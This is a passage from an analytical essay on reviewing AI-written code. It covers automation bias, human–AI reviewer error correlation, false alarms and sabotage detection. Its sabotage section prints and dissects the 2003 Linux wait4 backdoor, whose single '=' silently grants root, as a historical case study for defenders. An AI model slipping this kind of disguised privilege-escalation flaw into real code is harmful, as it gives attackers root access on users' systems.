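Fourteen participants used the prompt in their review. Five treated it as a requirement and went back and forth between it and the code, seven read it as an explanation of the code, and two did both. Reviewers who treat the prompt as a requirement can check the code against it, while those who read it as an explanation risk assuming that the code does what the prompt says, just as they might when trusting a function's name.

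Twelve of the 32 said they looked for different things in labelled code. Those who trusted AI more tended to look for poor style, and those who trusted it less looked for faulty logic. One test manager expected AI to make fewer logical errors than people and claimed to pay little attention to AI-written code, but spent longer on the two labelled files. If trust does harm, it may do so by changing what people look for, which reading times don't measure.

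*Where AI Use Is Normalized, Author Seniority but Not AI Disclosure Biases Code Review* (Butler, Murphy-Hill and colleagues, 2026) describes a much larger experiment at Microsoft. In it, 447 of the company's engineers reviewed four snippets, three of which contained planted bugs. A note beside each snippet gave the author's seniority and whether the author had used AI. Disclosing AI use had no detectable effect on how the engineers rated the code or its author, or on how many comments they left.

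Seniority did affect the ratings. The engineers judged the same code to be slightly worse, less readable and less secure when it was attributed to a junior engineer. So information about an author can change how people see code. But 98% of these engineers used AI to write code themselves, so they probably learned little from hearing that someone else had. Some may also have missed the note, since the researchers didn't check who had read it. Like Khojah and colleagues, the researchers didn't measure how many bugs people found.

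*The effect of complexity and provenance on code review decisions* (2026) comes closer to measuring missed bugs. Its 385 participants reviewed a change and decided whether to accept a proposed revision, which was sometimes wrong. Labelling the revision as AI-written had no statistically supported effect on their decisions. But they accepted wrong revisions significantly more often when the code was complex, regardless of how the revisions were labelled.

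According to *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026), 28 people checked and repaired generated code in a 2024 experiment. Those who knew that a model had written the code searched more, verified more and made better repairs.

None of the four experiments found that people became less careful when they thought an AI had written the code. This is good evidence against the simplest version of the automation-bias argument. It doesn't rule out the rest of Spinellis's case, because an experiment that changes only the label can't show whether real AI-written code is harder to review. The result for complex code suggests that if agents write more convoluted code than people do, reviewers will accept more mistakes even without any special trust in AI. Short experiments also can't show whether people grow complacent after months of reviewing an agent's work.

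### What reviewers say they do

Rahman, Alam and colleagues surveyed 239 practitioners from 31 countries, most of whom had reviewed at least ten AI-authored pull requests. Each person answered matching questions about human and AI authors.

| Reported view or practice | Human author | AI author |
|---|---|---|
| High or very high initial trust in the code | 52.7% | 15.5% |
| Approves mainly after reasoning through all critical cases | 28.5% | 55.2% |
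| Approves mainly because tests cover the risky behaviour | 41.0% | 23.8% |
| Blocks the change if a doubt remains | 19.4% | 43.9% |
| Runs or inspects tests to check difficult logic | 52.1% | 65.0% |
| Simulates difficult logic mentally | 56.4% | 46.2% |

The respondents also ranked eight review activities by how much time they spend on each. When an AI wrote the code, working out the intent from the description fell in the ranking and running the code rose. If these answers are accurate, people rely less on apparent intent when reviewing AI-written code, as the `has_paid` example suggests they should.

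The last two rows of the table are harder to interpret. More people wanted to reason through the critical cases themselves, but fewer said they simulated the logic in their heads, the most direct form of literal reading. They may have meant running the code and reasoning about the results, which would help little if they only reran the agent's own tests.

Reviewers were also more suspicious of AI in another study. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) asked people whether they would accept, without asking for more explanation, a change that had passed its automated checks. The largest gap was for refactoring, which reorganizes code and is supposed to leave its behaviour unchanged. 146 respondents were less willing to accept an AI's refactoring than a person's, and only 21 were more willing. The question about AI always came second and was worded differently, so the true gap is probably smaller.

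People don't always review code the way they say they do. Many of Khojah and colleagues' participants said they read labelled code more thoroughly, but apart from the extra time, their eye movements showed no sign of it. In a survey of 116 people reported in *Why Johnny Can't Vibe* (2026), only 25% said they read every line of AI-generated code before running it, and about a third endorsed behaviours associated with automation bias. All but one had accepted AI code that later turned out to have a subtle bug, though most experienced programmers could probably say the same about their colleagues' code.

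Spinellis's concern about junior programmers remains untested. Rahman, Alam and colleagues found that people trusted AI-written code less at every level of experience, but we can't infer from this who misses more bugs.

### What reviewers do on GitHub

Most of the field evidence comes from AIDev, a public collection of agents' pull requests on GitHub up to August 2025. Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues (2026), in *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For*, found no recorded review for 61% of 33,596 agent pull requests. Some of that 61% may still have been reviewed, because a maintainer can read a change and merge it without leaving a comment.

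A comparison within the same repositories is more informative. These figures, calculated from Duma and colleagues' counts, include pull requests that received no review.

| | Agents' pull requests | People's pull requests |
|---|---|---|
| Reviewed by anyone, human or AI | 71.1% | 65.5% |
| Reviewed by at least one person | 30.1% | 30.8% |
| Reviewed only by people | 5.7% | 16.5% |
| People's review comments per pull request | 0.43 | 0.74 |

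People took part in reviewing almost the same share of both groups. They wrote fewer review comments on agents' work, and about a quarter of everything they wrote there was an instruction to an AI tool, such as telling it to fix a failed check. The comments in the last row also include remarks like "thanks", which Duma and colleagues counted as review. People therefore seem to have spent less of their effort evaluating the code when an agent wrote it.

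Comment counts can also mislead. *How Do AI Coding Agents Contribute to Software Development?* (2026) found that pull requests from four of five agents received more comments than those from people, and interpreted this as a sign that reviewers were more engaged. But in Duma and colleagues' data, AI tools wrote 72% of the comments on agents' pull requests. Agents' changes were also merged faster on average, which could mean that reviewers were confident or careless. Agarwal and colleagues point out that studies using AIDev reach different conclusions about whether agents' changes take more effort to review, depending on which agents and repositories they include.

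In *Habituation at the Gate*, Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026) looked for growing complacency by following 400 people who had each reviewed at least ten agent pull requests. Reviewers approved 27.9% of the changes in the first tenth of their reviews and 42.4% in the last tenth. Over the same span, their comments fell from 1.01 to 0.79 per review. Approval of human pull requests in the same repositories fell during those months, so reviewers weren't becoming more lenient in general.

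Yu and colleagues think the most likely explanation is habituation, in which people inspect less after many uneventful reviews. Their main evidence is that reviewers whose approval rates rose tended to write fewer comments. But a reviewer who finds nothing wrong has little to write, so we would see the same pattern if the agents improved or if people learned which tasks to give them. Yu and colleagues acknowledge that they couldn't measure the quality of the code. Their results are compatible with automation bias that develops slowly, but a convincing test would require planting similar bugs early and late in a reviewer's experience and comparing how often the reviewer missed them.

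### The flaws that reach reviewers

Early models made some mistakes that people rarely make. Tambon, Moradi Dakhel and colleagues (2024), in *Bugs in Large Language Models Generated Code*, sorted 333 bugs from three Codex-era models into ten patterns, though the study is now mainly of historical interest. In one example, the prompt asked for a function that lists a program's command-line options, separated by spaces. Codex wrote reasonable code but also sorted the options, an unrequested step that made the result wrong. Tambon and colleagues believe that a human programmer would seldom do this, but they had no sample of human bugs for comparison.

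Other early bugs, such as syntax errors and unfinished functions, were much easier to catch. More recent models still make some obvious mistakes. Rahman (2026), in *From Observation to Explanation*, tested seven models on Python classes from real projects and found that only 24% to 35% of their answers were correct. Many of the failures were crashes, caused for example by references to attributes that didn't exist. An agent that runs its code will usually find and fix a crash before anyone reviews the change, so the remaining mistakes are more likely to resemble `has_paid`, where the code runs without crashing but does the wrong thing.

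Reviewers' complaints fit this explanation. Of the 158 people who told Rahman, Alam and colleagues that AI-written changes were harder to approve, 64 mentioned missing knowledge of the project, 46 mentioned code that looks right but isn't, and 43 mentioned needless complexity, duplication or poor maintainability. Knowing about an undocumented business rule may therefore help a reviewer more than reading the code literally.

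If flaws in AI-written code are unusually hard to see, people should have to correct that code more often after it is merged. *Will It Survive?* (Rahman, Begoug and Shihab, 2026) followed about 649,000 lines from 2,794 merged pull requests until the end of 2025. With each pull request weighted equally, 28.0% of agents' lines had been changed or deleted, compared with 34.5% of people's lines in the same repositories. Bug fixes made up 35.6% of the later commits that changed agents' code and 32.5% of those that changed people's code, a difference too small to distinguish from chance.

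*From Observation to Explanation*, a doctoral summary by the same lead author, reports a larger gap for Devin, an agent that works with relatively little supervision. Bug fixes made up 49.1% of the changes to Devin's code and 37.9% of the changes to human code. Rahman suggests that such agents write plausible code that passes review but needs correcting later. The two results don't necessarily conflict, because the study with the smaller gap combines five agents. Devin may be worse than the others, or the results may differ because of which projects were chosen and how changes were classified.

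Rahman, Begoug and Shihab identified the purpose of each change from keywords in its description, and that classification is sensitive to how the keywords are matched. When they let keywords match parts of longer words, "auth" matched the "Co-authored-by" line that agents add, and the share of agent-code changes that counted as testing or security work rose from 3.9% to 29.7%.

These studies also count only the bugs that somebody fixed. A shop where nearly every order has one invoice might run `has_paid` for years without noticing anything wrong. If reviewers check AI-written code more carefully, as they say they do, similar correction rates could also hide a difference in how hard the code is to review. Testing this would require an experiment in which people look for known bugs in agents' code and in comparable human code, without knowing which is which. None of the experiments described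 here did this.

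## Combining a human and an AI reviewer

A second reviewer helps only with bugs that the first one misses. A model that finds most bugs adds little if the human reviewer has already found the same ones, while a person who finds relatively few may still add a lot if the model missed them. The gain depends on how often each reviewer misses bugs and on how correlated their misses are. The correlation is much harder to measure.

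### The chance that both miss a bug

Let *h* be the human's miss rate and *a* the AI's. Each reviewer scores 1 for a bug they miss and 0 for a bug they find, so their average scores are *h* and *a*. The product of the two scores is 1 only when both reviewers miss the bug, so its average is the joint miss rate, *J*.

The covariance of the scores, which measures how far they rise and fall together, is the average of the product minus the product of the averages, or *J* − *ha*. Correlation (*ρ*) is the covariance divided by both standard deviations, which are √(*h*(1 − *h*)) and √(*a*(1 − *a*)) for scores of 0 and 1. Rearranging gives

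*J* = *ha* + *ρ* √(*h*(1 − *h*)*a*(1 − *a*))

Suppose the human misses half of all bugs and the AI misses 30%. The product of the miss rates is 0.15, and the square-root term is about 0.23. Out of 100 bugs, the AI misses 30, and the table shows how many of those the human catches.

| Error correlation | Chance that both miss a bug | AI's 30 misses that the human catches |
|---|---|---|
| −0.3 | 0.08 | 22 |
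| 0 | 0.15 | 15 |
| 0.4 | 0.24 | 6 |
| 0.65 (the highest possible here) | 0.30 | 0 |

The same person catches nearly four times as many of the bugs the model misses at a correlation of −0.3 as at 0.4. A more accurate second reviewer isn't always better. If the team replaced the human with a second model that missed only 20% of bugs, but whose misses had a correlation of 0.5 with the first model's, the joint miss rate would be 0.15, no better than with a human who misses half the bugs independently of the first model.

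Reviewers who never communicate can still have correlated errors, because some bugs are harder for everyone. If half the bugs are easy and half are hard, and each reviewer misses 10% of the easy ones and 90% of the hard ones, each misses half overall. Together they miss 41% of the bugs, well above the 25% we would get by multiplying their overall miss rates.

This could reverse if the two reviewers read the code differently. Suppose half the bugs are like `all_paid`, where tracing the loop reveals the mistake, and half are like `has_paid`, where the code matches its comment but the shop wanted something else. A model that traces well might miss 10% of the first kind and 90% of the second, while a person who knows the shop might do the opposite. Each still misses half of all bugs, but only 9% get past both.

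The evidence so far doesn't support a strongly negative correlation between human and model errors, as there would be if people read for intent and models read literally. When students and reasoning models predicted the output of the same 20 functions, they tended to struggle with the same ones. Pairing a human and an AI reviewer may therefore work less well than it would if they read code so differently.

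### Estimating how many bugs remain

The overlap between two reviewers' findings can help estimate how many bugs both missed in a real project, where nobody can count them directly. Suppose one reviewer finds 12 bugs, the other finds 15, and 6 appear on both lists. The second reviewer found 6 of the first reviewer's 12 bugs, or half. If the second reviewer also found half of all the bugs, there are 30 in total. Together the reviewers found 12 + 15 − 6 = 21, so they missed 9.

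This is capture-recapture, a method ecologists use to estimate animal populations. The basic estimate is *n*₁*n*₂/*m*, where *n*₁ and *n*₂ are the numbers of bugs each reviewer found and *m* is the number both found. *"Not Used Elsewhere" Is Not "Unused" in a Lean Formalization* (2026) uses a version called the Chapman estimate, (*n*₁ + 1)(*n*₂ + 1)/(*m* + 1) − 1, which gives about 29 bugs here. The same paper traces the method's use in software inspection to Eick and colleagues, who applied it to 13 reviews of requirements and designs but couldn't check the estimates because they didn't know the true number of defects.

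The method assumes that one reviewer is no more likely to find a bug when the other has found it. Shared blind spots break this assumption. If the program also contained 20 bugs like `has_paid`, and both reviewers missed them because neither knew what the shop wanted, the two lists would still contain 12 and 15 bugs, with 6 on both. The estimate would still be 30, but the true total would be 50.

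Even a moderate positive correlation makes the formula greatly underestimate how many bugs remain. With 100 bugs, the same miss rates as before, and a correlation of 0.4, the human finds 50 bugs and the AI finds 70, with about 44 found by both. The formula then estimates a total of 79 or 80. The reviewers have found 76 between them, so the estimate implies that only three or four remain, when there are really 24. A negative correlation makes the estimate too high.

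More reviewers help somewhat. *Effective Automated Decision Support for Managing Crowdtesting* (2018) describes versions of the method that allow for differences in how hard bugs are to find, how good reviewers are, or both. *Predicting Defect Content and Quality Assurance Effectiveness* (2014) gives four inspectors as the minimum for suitable estimates. Running one model four times wouldn't serve the purpose of that minimum, because a bug the model can't recognize will probably be missing from all four lists.

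An AI reviewer's false alarms also inflate the estimate, because they lengthen its list without adding to the overlap. If 5 of the AI's 15 reports were wrong, the estimate should have been 12 × 10/6 = 20 bugs, not 30. Someone also has to decide when two comments describe the same bug. Treating different bugs as one makes the estimate too low, and failing to match two descriptions of one bug makes it too high. A team could reasonably treat a small overlap as a warning that bugs remain, but a large overlap between reviewers who tend to find the same bugs is only weak evidence that few remain.

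### Whether two models count as two reviewers

A second model is cheaper than a human reviewer, so it matters whether it misses different things from the first. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) measured how often two models chose the same wrong answer when both got a multiple-choice question wrong. Agreement was substantially higher for accurate models and for models from the same developer or with the same underlying architecture. The result suggests that what models miss may become more alike as they improve, although choosing the same wrong answer isn't the same as missing the same bug.

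*The Specification as Quality Gate* (2026) reports a small test in which four AI products reviewed five Python functions, each with one planted bug, for 100 reviews in total. Detection ranged from 0% to 100%, depending on the model family and on how much specialist knowledge the bug required. In an earlier round, Claude reviewed a function that calculates interest rates between known points. In all five reviews, it raised a concern about sorting, missed that the interpolation method was wrong, and declared the code correct. Repeating the review didn't help, apparently because Claude couldn't identify which method the author wanted. Two of the four products in the later test ran on Claude models, so a team that buys two AI reviewers won't necessarily get two different models.

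Models of different sizes can notice different things. *More Effort or a Different Model?* (2026) gave three Claude models patches that looked plausible but were wrong. The larger models, Opus and Sonnet, complained of missing functionality 9 and 10 times, and the smaller Haiku did so once. Haiku asked for more tests 10 times and Opus twice. But Haiku would be a poor choice for catching missing functionality that Opus overlooked.

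Models may also find different problems and still have positively correlated errors. *AI Cannot Review What Humans Catch* (2026) tested three AI reviewers on changes to agent instruction files, which tell coding agents how to work on a project. Human reviewers had raised 1,912 concerns that experts judged valid. OpenCode reproduced 75 of these, Claude 62 and Codex 25, and only three were reproduced by all three AI reviewers.

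When reviewers find so little, their lists will hardly overlap even by chance, so the small overlap here is weak evidence of variety. If the three had worked independently at those rates, they would have found about 158 concerns between them, but they found 132 (6.9%), so their lists overlapped more than chance predicts. In 347 of the 446 pull requests, none of the three found any human concern.

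The people were much more likely than the AI reviewers to comment on something missing. Such comments made up 24.6% of the people's comments and 5.4% of the AI reviewers' comments in ordinary use. The AI reviewers were more likely to mention formatting. This fits the idea that people contribute knowledge of what a project needs. However, instruction files are mostly prose and have no output to trace, so they give a literal reader little chance to show what it does well.

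### Trials of people and models together

OpenAI's 2024 trial, now mainly of historical interest, shows what can happen when people start from a model's list of problems. In *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs*, contractors with a median of five years' Python experience reviewed code written by ChatGPT. Some started from a review written by CriticGPT, a model trained to criticize code. They could keep, edit or delete its comments and add their own.

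The human-AI teams wrote much more comprehensive reviews than people working alone, but no more comprehensive than the model's own. Their reviews also included fewer invented bugs and trivial complaints than the model's. People often deleted the model's comments and less often added new ones, so they were more useful for removing false alarms than for finding what the model had missed.

OpenAI also looked at answers, mostly not code, that one contractor had rated flawless. When the critic reported a problem in such an answer and a contractor considered its criticism, 24% of the answers turned out to have a problem that substantially lowered their rating. A second contractor without the critic rated "flawless" answers that poorly only 6% of the time. The comparison favours the critic, because the 24% covers only answers in which it had reported a problem, but the gap may also mean that two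 people share more blind spots than a person and a model do.

In *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews*, Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues (2024) ran a better test of whether a model helps people find known problems. They planted 48 issues, ranging from duplicated code to logic errors, in 12 small programs and recruited 29 developers, nearly all working professionals. The developers reviewed some programs unaided, some with a review by GPT-4, and some with a list that they believed an AI had written but that contained exactly the planted issues.

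Unaided developers found a median of 50% of the planted issues, and so did those who started with GPT-4's review. Yet GPT-4's reviews already contained 42% of the issues on average. If people had kept those and independently found half of the rest, they would have reached about 71%. (This combines a median with an average, so it is only a rough guide.)

Seeing GPT-4's list of issues apparently changed how developers read the code. They kept 89% of the issues it reported and commented mostly on the lines it had mentioned. Across 24 reviews in each group, developers without GPT-4's help commented on 484 different lines, and those with it commented on 371. In one program, GPT-4 missed a conversion to hexadecimal that used base 8 instead of 16. A person busy checking comments about other lines might also miss this sort of mistake.

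The trial was small enough to have missed a moderate benefit, and a current model would provide a much better list. With the perfect list, reviewers usually reported every planted issue. So people will accept good findings, but they may search less for issues the AI left out. This reduced searching overlaps with automation bias, although the developers weren't approving code because an AI had judged it correct.

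Larger samples come from comparing a model's comments with people's comments in real reviews. In *Studying Quality Improvements Recommended via Manual and Automated Code Review*, Crupi, Tufano and Bavota (2026) collected 447 useful human comments from 179 pull requests and asked GPT-4 Turbo to review the same files. The model raised only 10% of the points people had raised. The researchers checked 292 of its 1,189 other comments and considered about 40% of those they checked meaningful.

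This suggests that the model and the human reviewers complement each other, but it can't show that either missed the other's points. Many comments concerned style or structure, and a reviewer may notice an awkward name and decide not to mention it. The model and the reviewers were probably looking for different things, so the capture-recapture formula doesn't apply. With these figures, it would imply more than 5,000 worthwhile comments on those 179 pull requests, which seems unlikely.

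A test on the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, measured bug detection more directly. Sashiko is an AI system that reviews proposed kernel changes in stages. One stage checks whether the code matches its description, and another traces how the code runs. The test used the bugs behind the latest 1,000 kernel changes labelled as fixes, and human reviewers had missed all of these bugs. Using Gemini 3.1 Pro, Sashiko found 53.6% of them, according to the Linux Foundation's *Sashiko* documentation.

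The AI therefore missed 46.4% of the bugs that people had missed, so adding it could have prevented just over half of them if developers had acted on its reports. This rate is more useful than the AI's overall miss rate, but it doesn't give the error correlation, because we don't know what share of the bugs caught by people the AI would miss. The correlation would be positive if that share were 30% and negative if it were 60%. The sample also leaves out any bugs that nobody has found yet.

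*The End of Code Review* (2026) argues that coding agents make human inspection unnecessary because they can consider the full file, its history, the tests and the documentation together, fix what they find, and work at 3 am without losing focus. The paper adds that agents detect the same categories of defect as people. But two reviewers can both be good at finding logic errors and still miss different ones. Access to more documents also won't help an agent review `has_paid` if nobody wrote down that some orders have two invoices.

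### Directing a fuzzer

People and models can also combine their judgement to guide fuzzers, which test programs automatically. Luu, Pasdar and colleagues (2026) studied this with the programming language PHP in *Following Dragons*. Fuzzers usually keep an input for further experiments if it makes the program run new code, so they miss bugs that depend on an unusual value rather than an unusual path through the code.

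One such bug involved the memory set aside for fibers, tasks that PHP can pause and resume. A malformed setting such as `9690x-D` passed PHP's checks but later caused a crash. Most settings run through the same code, so an ordinary fuzzer was unlikely to keep trying new ones. Years earlier, in a code review, PHP's developers had discussed the risk of running out of this memory. Guided by that discussion, a researcher added an annotation that made the fuzzer count each new memory size as progress, and the fuzzer found the crash.

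The researcher, a doctoral student who didn't know PHP's code, annotated 37 functions in this way using old review comments. Gemini 2.5 Flash then annotated the same functions. The fuzzer ran for 24 hours on each of the 34 versions of PHP that contained them.

| Annotations | Distinct crashes found |
|---|---|
| Written by the student | 31 |
| Written by the model | 24 |
| Found with both | 15 |
| Found only with the student's | 16 |
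| Found only with the model's | 9 |

Using both sets of annotations exposed 40 crashes, 29% more than using the student's alone. Some of the extra nine may be due to chance, because fuzzing is random and a second run with the student's annotations alone would also have found some new crashes. Capture-recapture gives an estimate of about 50 crashes in all, which is probably too low because both sets covered the same functions and were tested with the same fuzzer.

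The model's greater advantage was coverage. The student could match only 37 of 117 security-related comments to a function. When the model did the whole job, it annotated 117 functions and the fuzzer found 47 crashes. However, the model was less accurate than the student at choosing the right function, agreeing with the student's choice in only 18 of those 37 cases.

### Who reads first, and what they see

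A team with both a human and an AI reviewer has to decide what each one sees and when. Researchers have tested only some of the obvious arrangements.

| Arrangement | Evidence |
|---|---|
| The person starts from the AI's review | OpenAI and Tufano and colleagues tested it with people |
| The person reviews first, then sees the AI's comments | Tufano and colleagues recommend it but didn't test it |
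| A second AI works without seeing the first review | Kwon (2026), in *We Fixed the Scorer First*, tested it on 24 planted defects |
| The reviewer writes down the intent before reading the code | None of the trials here tested it |
| The AI reviews code with the names hidden | Researchers tested models on related tasks, but not as part of a human-AI team |

Having the person review the code first is sensible. Once they have submitted their comments, the AI's list can't draw their attention away from the rest of the code, and anything new on the list is a gain. The person might still read less carefully if they know that an AI will check afterwards. This order also saves no human time, because the person does a full review and then checks the AI's comments.

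Kwon provides a little evidence for keeping reviews separate, though both reviewers were models. One AI pass found 14 of the 24 defects. A second pass raised the total to 18 when it saw the other reviewer's list and to 22 when it didn't. The difference between 18 and 22 could easily be due to chance. Even the rise from 14 to 22 fell just short of statistical significance after Kwon allowed for related results.

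Writing down the intent first is meant to stop a reviewer from guessing what a function does from its name. Before opening `all_paid`, the reviewer would read the request, write that one paid invoice and one unpaid invoice should return False, and then check the loop against that answer. The 2023 student comparison doesn't test this, because its participants described each function's purpose after seeing the code. A reviewer who misunderstands the request will write down the wrong answer, and may then reject correct code more confidently than usual.

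Some reviewers already do something similar. In the survey by Rahman and colleagues, people more often chose to rewrite part of a change themselves when checking difficult logic from an AI. Reviewers who write their version before studying the agent's have to form their own idea of how the code should work.

Another possibility is to let the model describe the code and the person judge the description. *Guiding Human Validation of LLM-Generated Code via Verifiable Literate Programming* found that, of the bugs visible in such a description, a user could identify 86% to 91% from one line and a few lines around it. The description would have to be literal, however. "Returns True if at least one invoice is paid" would expose the bug in `has_paid`, whereas "checks that the customer has paid" would hide it. This method also misses most bugs that are hard to describe in terms of what the user wanted,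 such as passing the wrong argument to a library function.

### Hiding the names

Names can mislead a model about what code does, so hiding them might encourage a more literal reading. In the Face/Off experiments in *On the Lexical Superstition of Large Language Models for Code Comprehension* (2026), models chose between two descriptions of a program. DeepSeek-Coder-V2 was right 99.0% of the time with the original names, 98.6% with neutral placeholders and 78.7% with misleading names. But placeholders lowered GPT-3.5's accuracy from 92.8% to 81.4%, and they also made some stronger models less accurate in Le and colleagues' execution-prediction tests.

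The researchers trained smaller models on code without informative names. This made the models better at summarizing code with misleading names and worse at summarizing ordinary code. The researchers caution that their results don't establish when hiding names helps.

File names can have a similar influence. *What File-Level Hits Hide in Bug Localization* (2026) studied models that rank files by how likely they are to need changing for a reported bug. Models trained with samples of the code and models trained without them scored about the same when they could see the original file paths, but very differently when they couldn't. Plausible but wrong paths misled even models that could see some of the code. So a model can appear to be reading the code when it is mostly matching names.

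Comments may need to be hidden too. *Don't Judge Code by Its Cover* (2025) warns that a comment implying an expert wrote the code can lead a model to analyze it less thoroughly or not at all.

A review with the names hidden also hides evidence of what the code was meant to do, so it can't be the only review. A second step has to restore the names, or supply a separate specification, and compare either one with the model's report of what the code does. Hiding the names should help most with code like `all_paid`, but it wouldn't help with `has_paid`, where something other than the name and comment hides the mistake.

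### The cost of false alarms

Every AI report a person has to check uses time they could have spent reading the code. Because most changes don't contain a serious bug, even a fairly accurate reviewer can produce more false alarms than real findings.

Suppose that 50 of 1,000 changes contain a bug. The AI finds 35 of these and wrongly flags 10% of the other 950 changes. It produces 130 reports, and only 27% of them are right. If each report takes 20 minutes to check, the team spends about 43 hours, or 74 minutes per real bug found.

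The checking time per additional bug is higher, because the human would have found some of the bugs the AI finds anyway. Suppose the human again misses half of all bugs and takes 20 minutes to check each report, including reports of bugs they have already found. Each bug that only the AI finds then takes about 2 hours of checking at a correlation of −0.3, about 2½ hours at zero correlation, and nearly 3½ hours at 0.4.

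A team could reduce false alarms by acting only when both reviewers report the same problem, but with independent reviewers it would then miss 65% of all bugs instead of 15%. Asking the AI reviewer for more explanation may not help. In *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?*, Jin and Chen (2026) gave five models a requirement and either a correct or a buggy program, using more than 700 programming tasks. The models often rejected correct code, and they made more mistakes when the prompt also asked for an explanation and a fix. The prompts requested the verdict first, so the explanation came too late to improve it. The request for a fix may also have made the models more likely to report a problem.

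Jin and Chen suggest running tests on both the original program and the model's proposed fix. If the original passes, or the fix breaks something, the model's complaint is less credible. This can filter out false alarms without taking a person's time, but the tests have to reflect what people want. The agent's test for `has_paid`, for example, expects True when one invoice is paid, so the filter would throw out a correct complaint.

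Some false alarms are also disagreements about what the code should do. *More Effort or a Different Model?* found that most false alarms concerned behaviour that the official fix shared. The models may have required something nobody wanted, or flagged a fault that the maintainers had accepted. In another 163 reviews, the model approved the patch despite naming a specific concern about how it worked. A team that reads only the verdicts would miss those concerns, but reading them all would bring back much of the work the verdicts were supposed to save.

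Even accurate reports take time to check. In the trial by Tufano and colleagues, reviews took an average of 42 minutes unaided, 56 minutes when they started from GPT-4's comments, and 57 minutes when they started from the perfect list. The differences weren't statistically significant, but there was no sign that either list saved time. Reviews that started from GPT-4's comments were also longer, at 28 sentences instead of 16, which gives the code's author more to read.

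Linux developers have argued over whether Sashiko is worth this effort. Its documentation puts false alarms "well within" 20%, based on limited manual checks. *What's Actually in a Sashiko Review?* (2026) describes a dispute over a different figure, a hit rate of about 60%. Andrew Morton, who wants to make Sashiko mandatory in memory-management code review, cited it in Sashiko's favour. Lorenzo Stoakes objected that the figure is a share of reviews, not of comments. If ten reviews contain five comments each, and six of the reviews identify one real bug each, the hit rate is 60% but only 12% of the comments are right.

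In *Re: Introduce Sashiko* (2026), a kernel maintainer asked for false alarms to come down "a fair bit" before the system emailed its reviews, but was already checking its website. Someone in the discussion also asked for a collection of changes known to be correct, which would make false alarms easier to measure.

The developers of ext4, a Linux file system, tested Sashiko by first sending its reviews only to the maintainer and the people who wrote each change (Tso, 2026, *Re: Stop false review statements*). After seeing how many were wrong, they decided the reviews were useful enough to send to everyone on the ext4 mailing list.

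## Detecting deliberate flaws that look like correct code

The names and comments around an honest mistake are evidence of what the programmer intended. Whoever wrote `all_paid` wanted a function that checks every invoice, so a reviewer can test the loop against the function's name. Reviewers can't rely on this evidence in cases of sabotage, where someone deliberately puts a flaw into software and makes it look innocent. The saboteur knows what the code really does and can choose names, comments, tests and a description that suggest something else.

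When a flaw is deliberate, intended reading recovers only the purpose the saboteur wants the reader to see. A reader who infers what code does from its apparent purpose will sometimes be wrong about honest code, but a saboteur can cause that error on purpose. Models can be misled this way too, since they also rely on comments. The intent that matters is that of the people who own or use the software, and a reviewer has to learn it from somewhere other than the change.

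A saboteur can also choose which kind of flaw to plant. In the earlier example of two reviewers who find the same bugs hard, 41% of accidental bugs got past both. A saboteur who planted only hard bugs, which each reviewer misses 90% of the time, would get 81% of them past both. This strategy would not work against reviewers with opposite weaknesses, because every flaw is easy for one of them. A miss rate measured on accidental bugs can therefore greatly understate the miss rate for sabotage, and a low error correlation between reviewers helps even more against a saboteur than against accidental bugs.

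### The 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel

In 2003 Linux kernel developers kept the master copy of their code in a system called BitKeeper. Some disliked BitKeeper, so the project also offered a copy through another system, CVS. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) describes how somebody apparently broke into the CVS server and added two lines to `wait4`, a function that lets a program wait for something to happen.

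```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The first condition tests whether the program called `wait4` with a particular combination of options. `current->uid` is the program's user ID, and ID 0 belongs to root, the account allowed to do anything. `-EINVAL` is the kernel's code for an invalid argument.

According to Freedom to Tinker, an expert reading casually would take this for "innocuous error-checking code". On that reading, the function reports an error if a program running as root passes a forbidden combination of options. The code looks like such a check because it has an `if`, two conditions and an error code.

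But the second condition has one equals sign, not two, so it assigns a value instead of comparing values. When the options match, the kernel sets the program's user ID to 0, which makes the program run as root. The assignment has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the condition fails and the line with the error code never runs.

| Call to `wait4` | If the code had `==` | What the code does |
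|---|---|---|
| Any other options | Nothing | Nothing |
| These options, ordinary user | Nothing | The program becomes root, with no error |
| These options, already root | Sets an error code | The program stays root, with no error |

Literal reading exposes the flaw, and so does intended reading, unless the reader stops after recognizing an error check. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) points out that `wait4` has no reason to deal with the user ID. A commenter on Freedom to Tinker adds that the check would make no sense even with two equals signs, because it would forbid a harmless combination of options, and only for root.

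A nightly automatic comparison caught the flaw, not a person reading the code. Larry McVoy (2003) explained in *Re: BK2CVS problem* that BitMover, the company behind BitKeeper, checked the public CVS copy against one of its own. The check found a difference, and McVoy had repaired the copy within 24 hours. Freedom to Tinker and InfoQ emphasize another clue, that the change lacked the link to an approval record that every genuine change carried. Both clues concern where the lines came from and can be noticed without understanding C.

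People worked out what the lines did only after that. On the kernel's mailing list, one developer said they looked odd. Another, Chad Kitching, saw that they set the user ID to zero and that the next line made the error code useless anyway. McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that."

So McVoy already knew that the change was unauthorized and still missed the single equals sign. This is one anecdote, but it fits the hypothesis about human readers unusually well. McVoy could explain the difference between `=` and `==` as soon as someone pointed it out, so ignorance of C wasn't the problem. Kitching's reply shows that people can read literally when they have a reason to, though this is much easier with two suspicious lines than with a forty-file change.

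The flaw never reached a release, according to *CVE-2003-1161*, its entry in Debian's security records. McVoy thought the danger was that a developer using the CVS copy would unknowingly submit the two lines as part of a patch. The lines would then have come from a trusted person through the normal process, and a check on their origin might have found nothing wrong, so reading the code would have been the main defence left.

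Nobody knows who wrote the lines. Some commenters on Freedom to Tinker suggested a tired developer who had skipped the approval process, since typing `=` for `==` is a common slip. The apparent break-in and the pointlessness of the check make that hard to believe, but the typing error alone wouldn't prove sabotage. A reviewer can remove the line without knowing whether it was deliberate. The question matters afterwards, because if it was sabotage, the author's other changes need checking again, which is probably unnecessary if the author was just tired.

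### When the screen shows a different program

*Trojan Source* (Boucher and Anderson, 2021) showed that the text a reader sees may differ from the text the compiler processes, contrary to what literal reading assumes. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes invisible characters that control display order, because Hebrew and Arabic run from right to left and often share a line with English. Many code editors applied these characters when displaying code, while compilers generally processed the text in its stored order.

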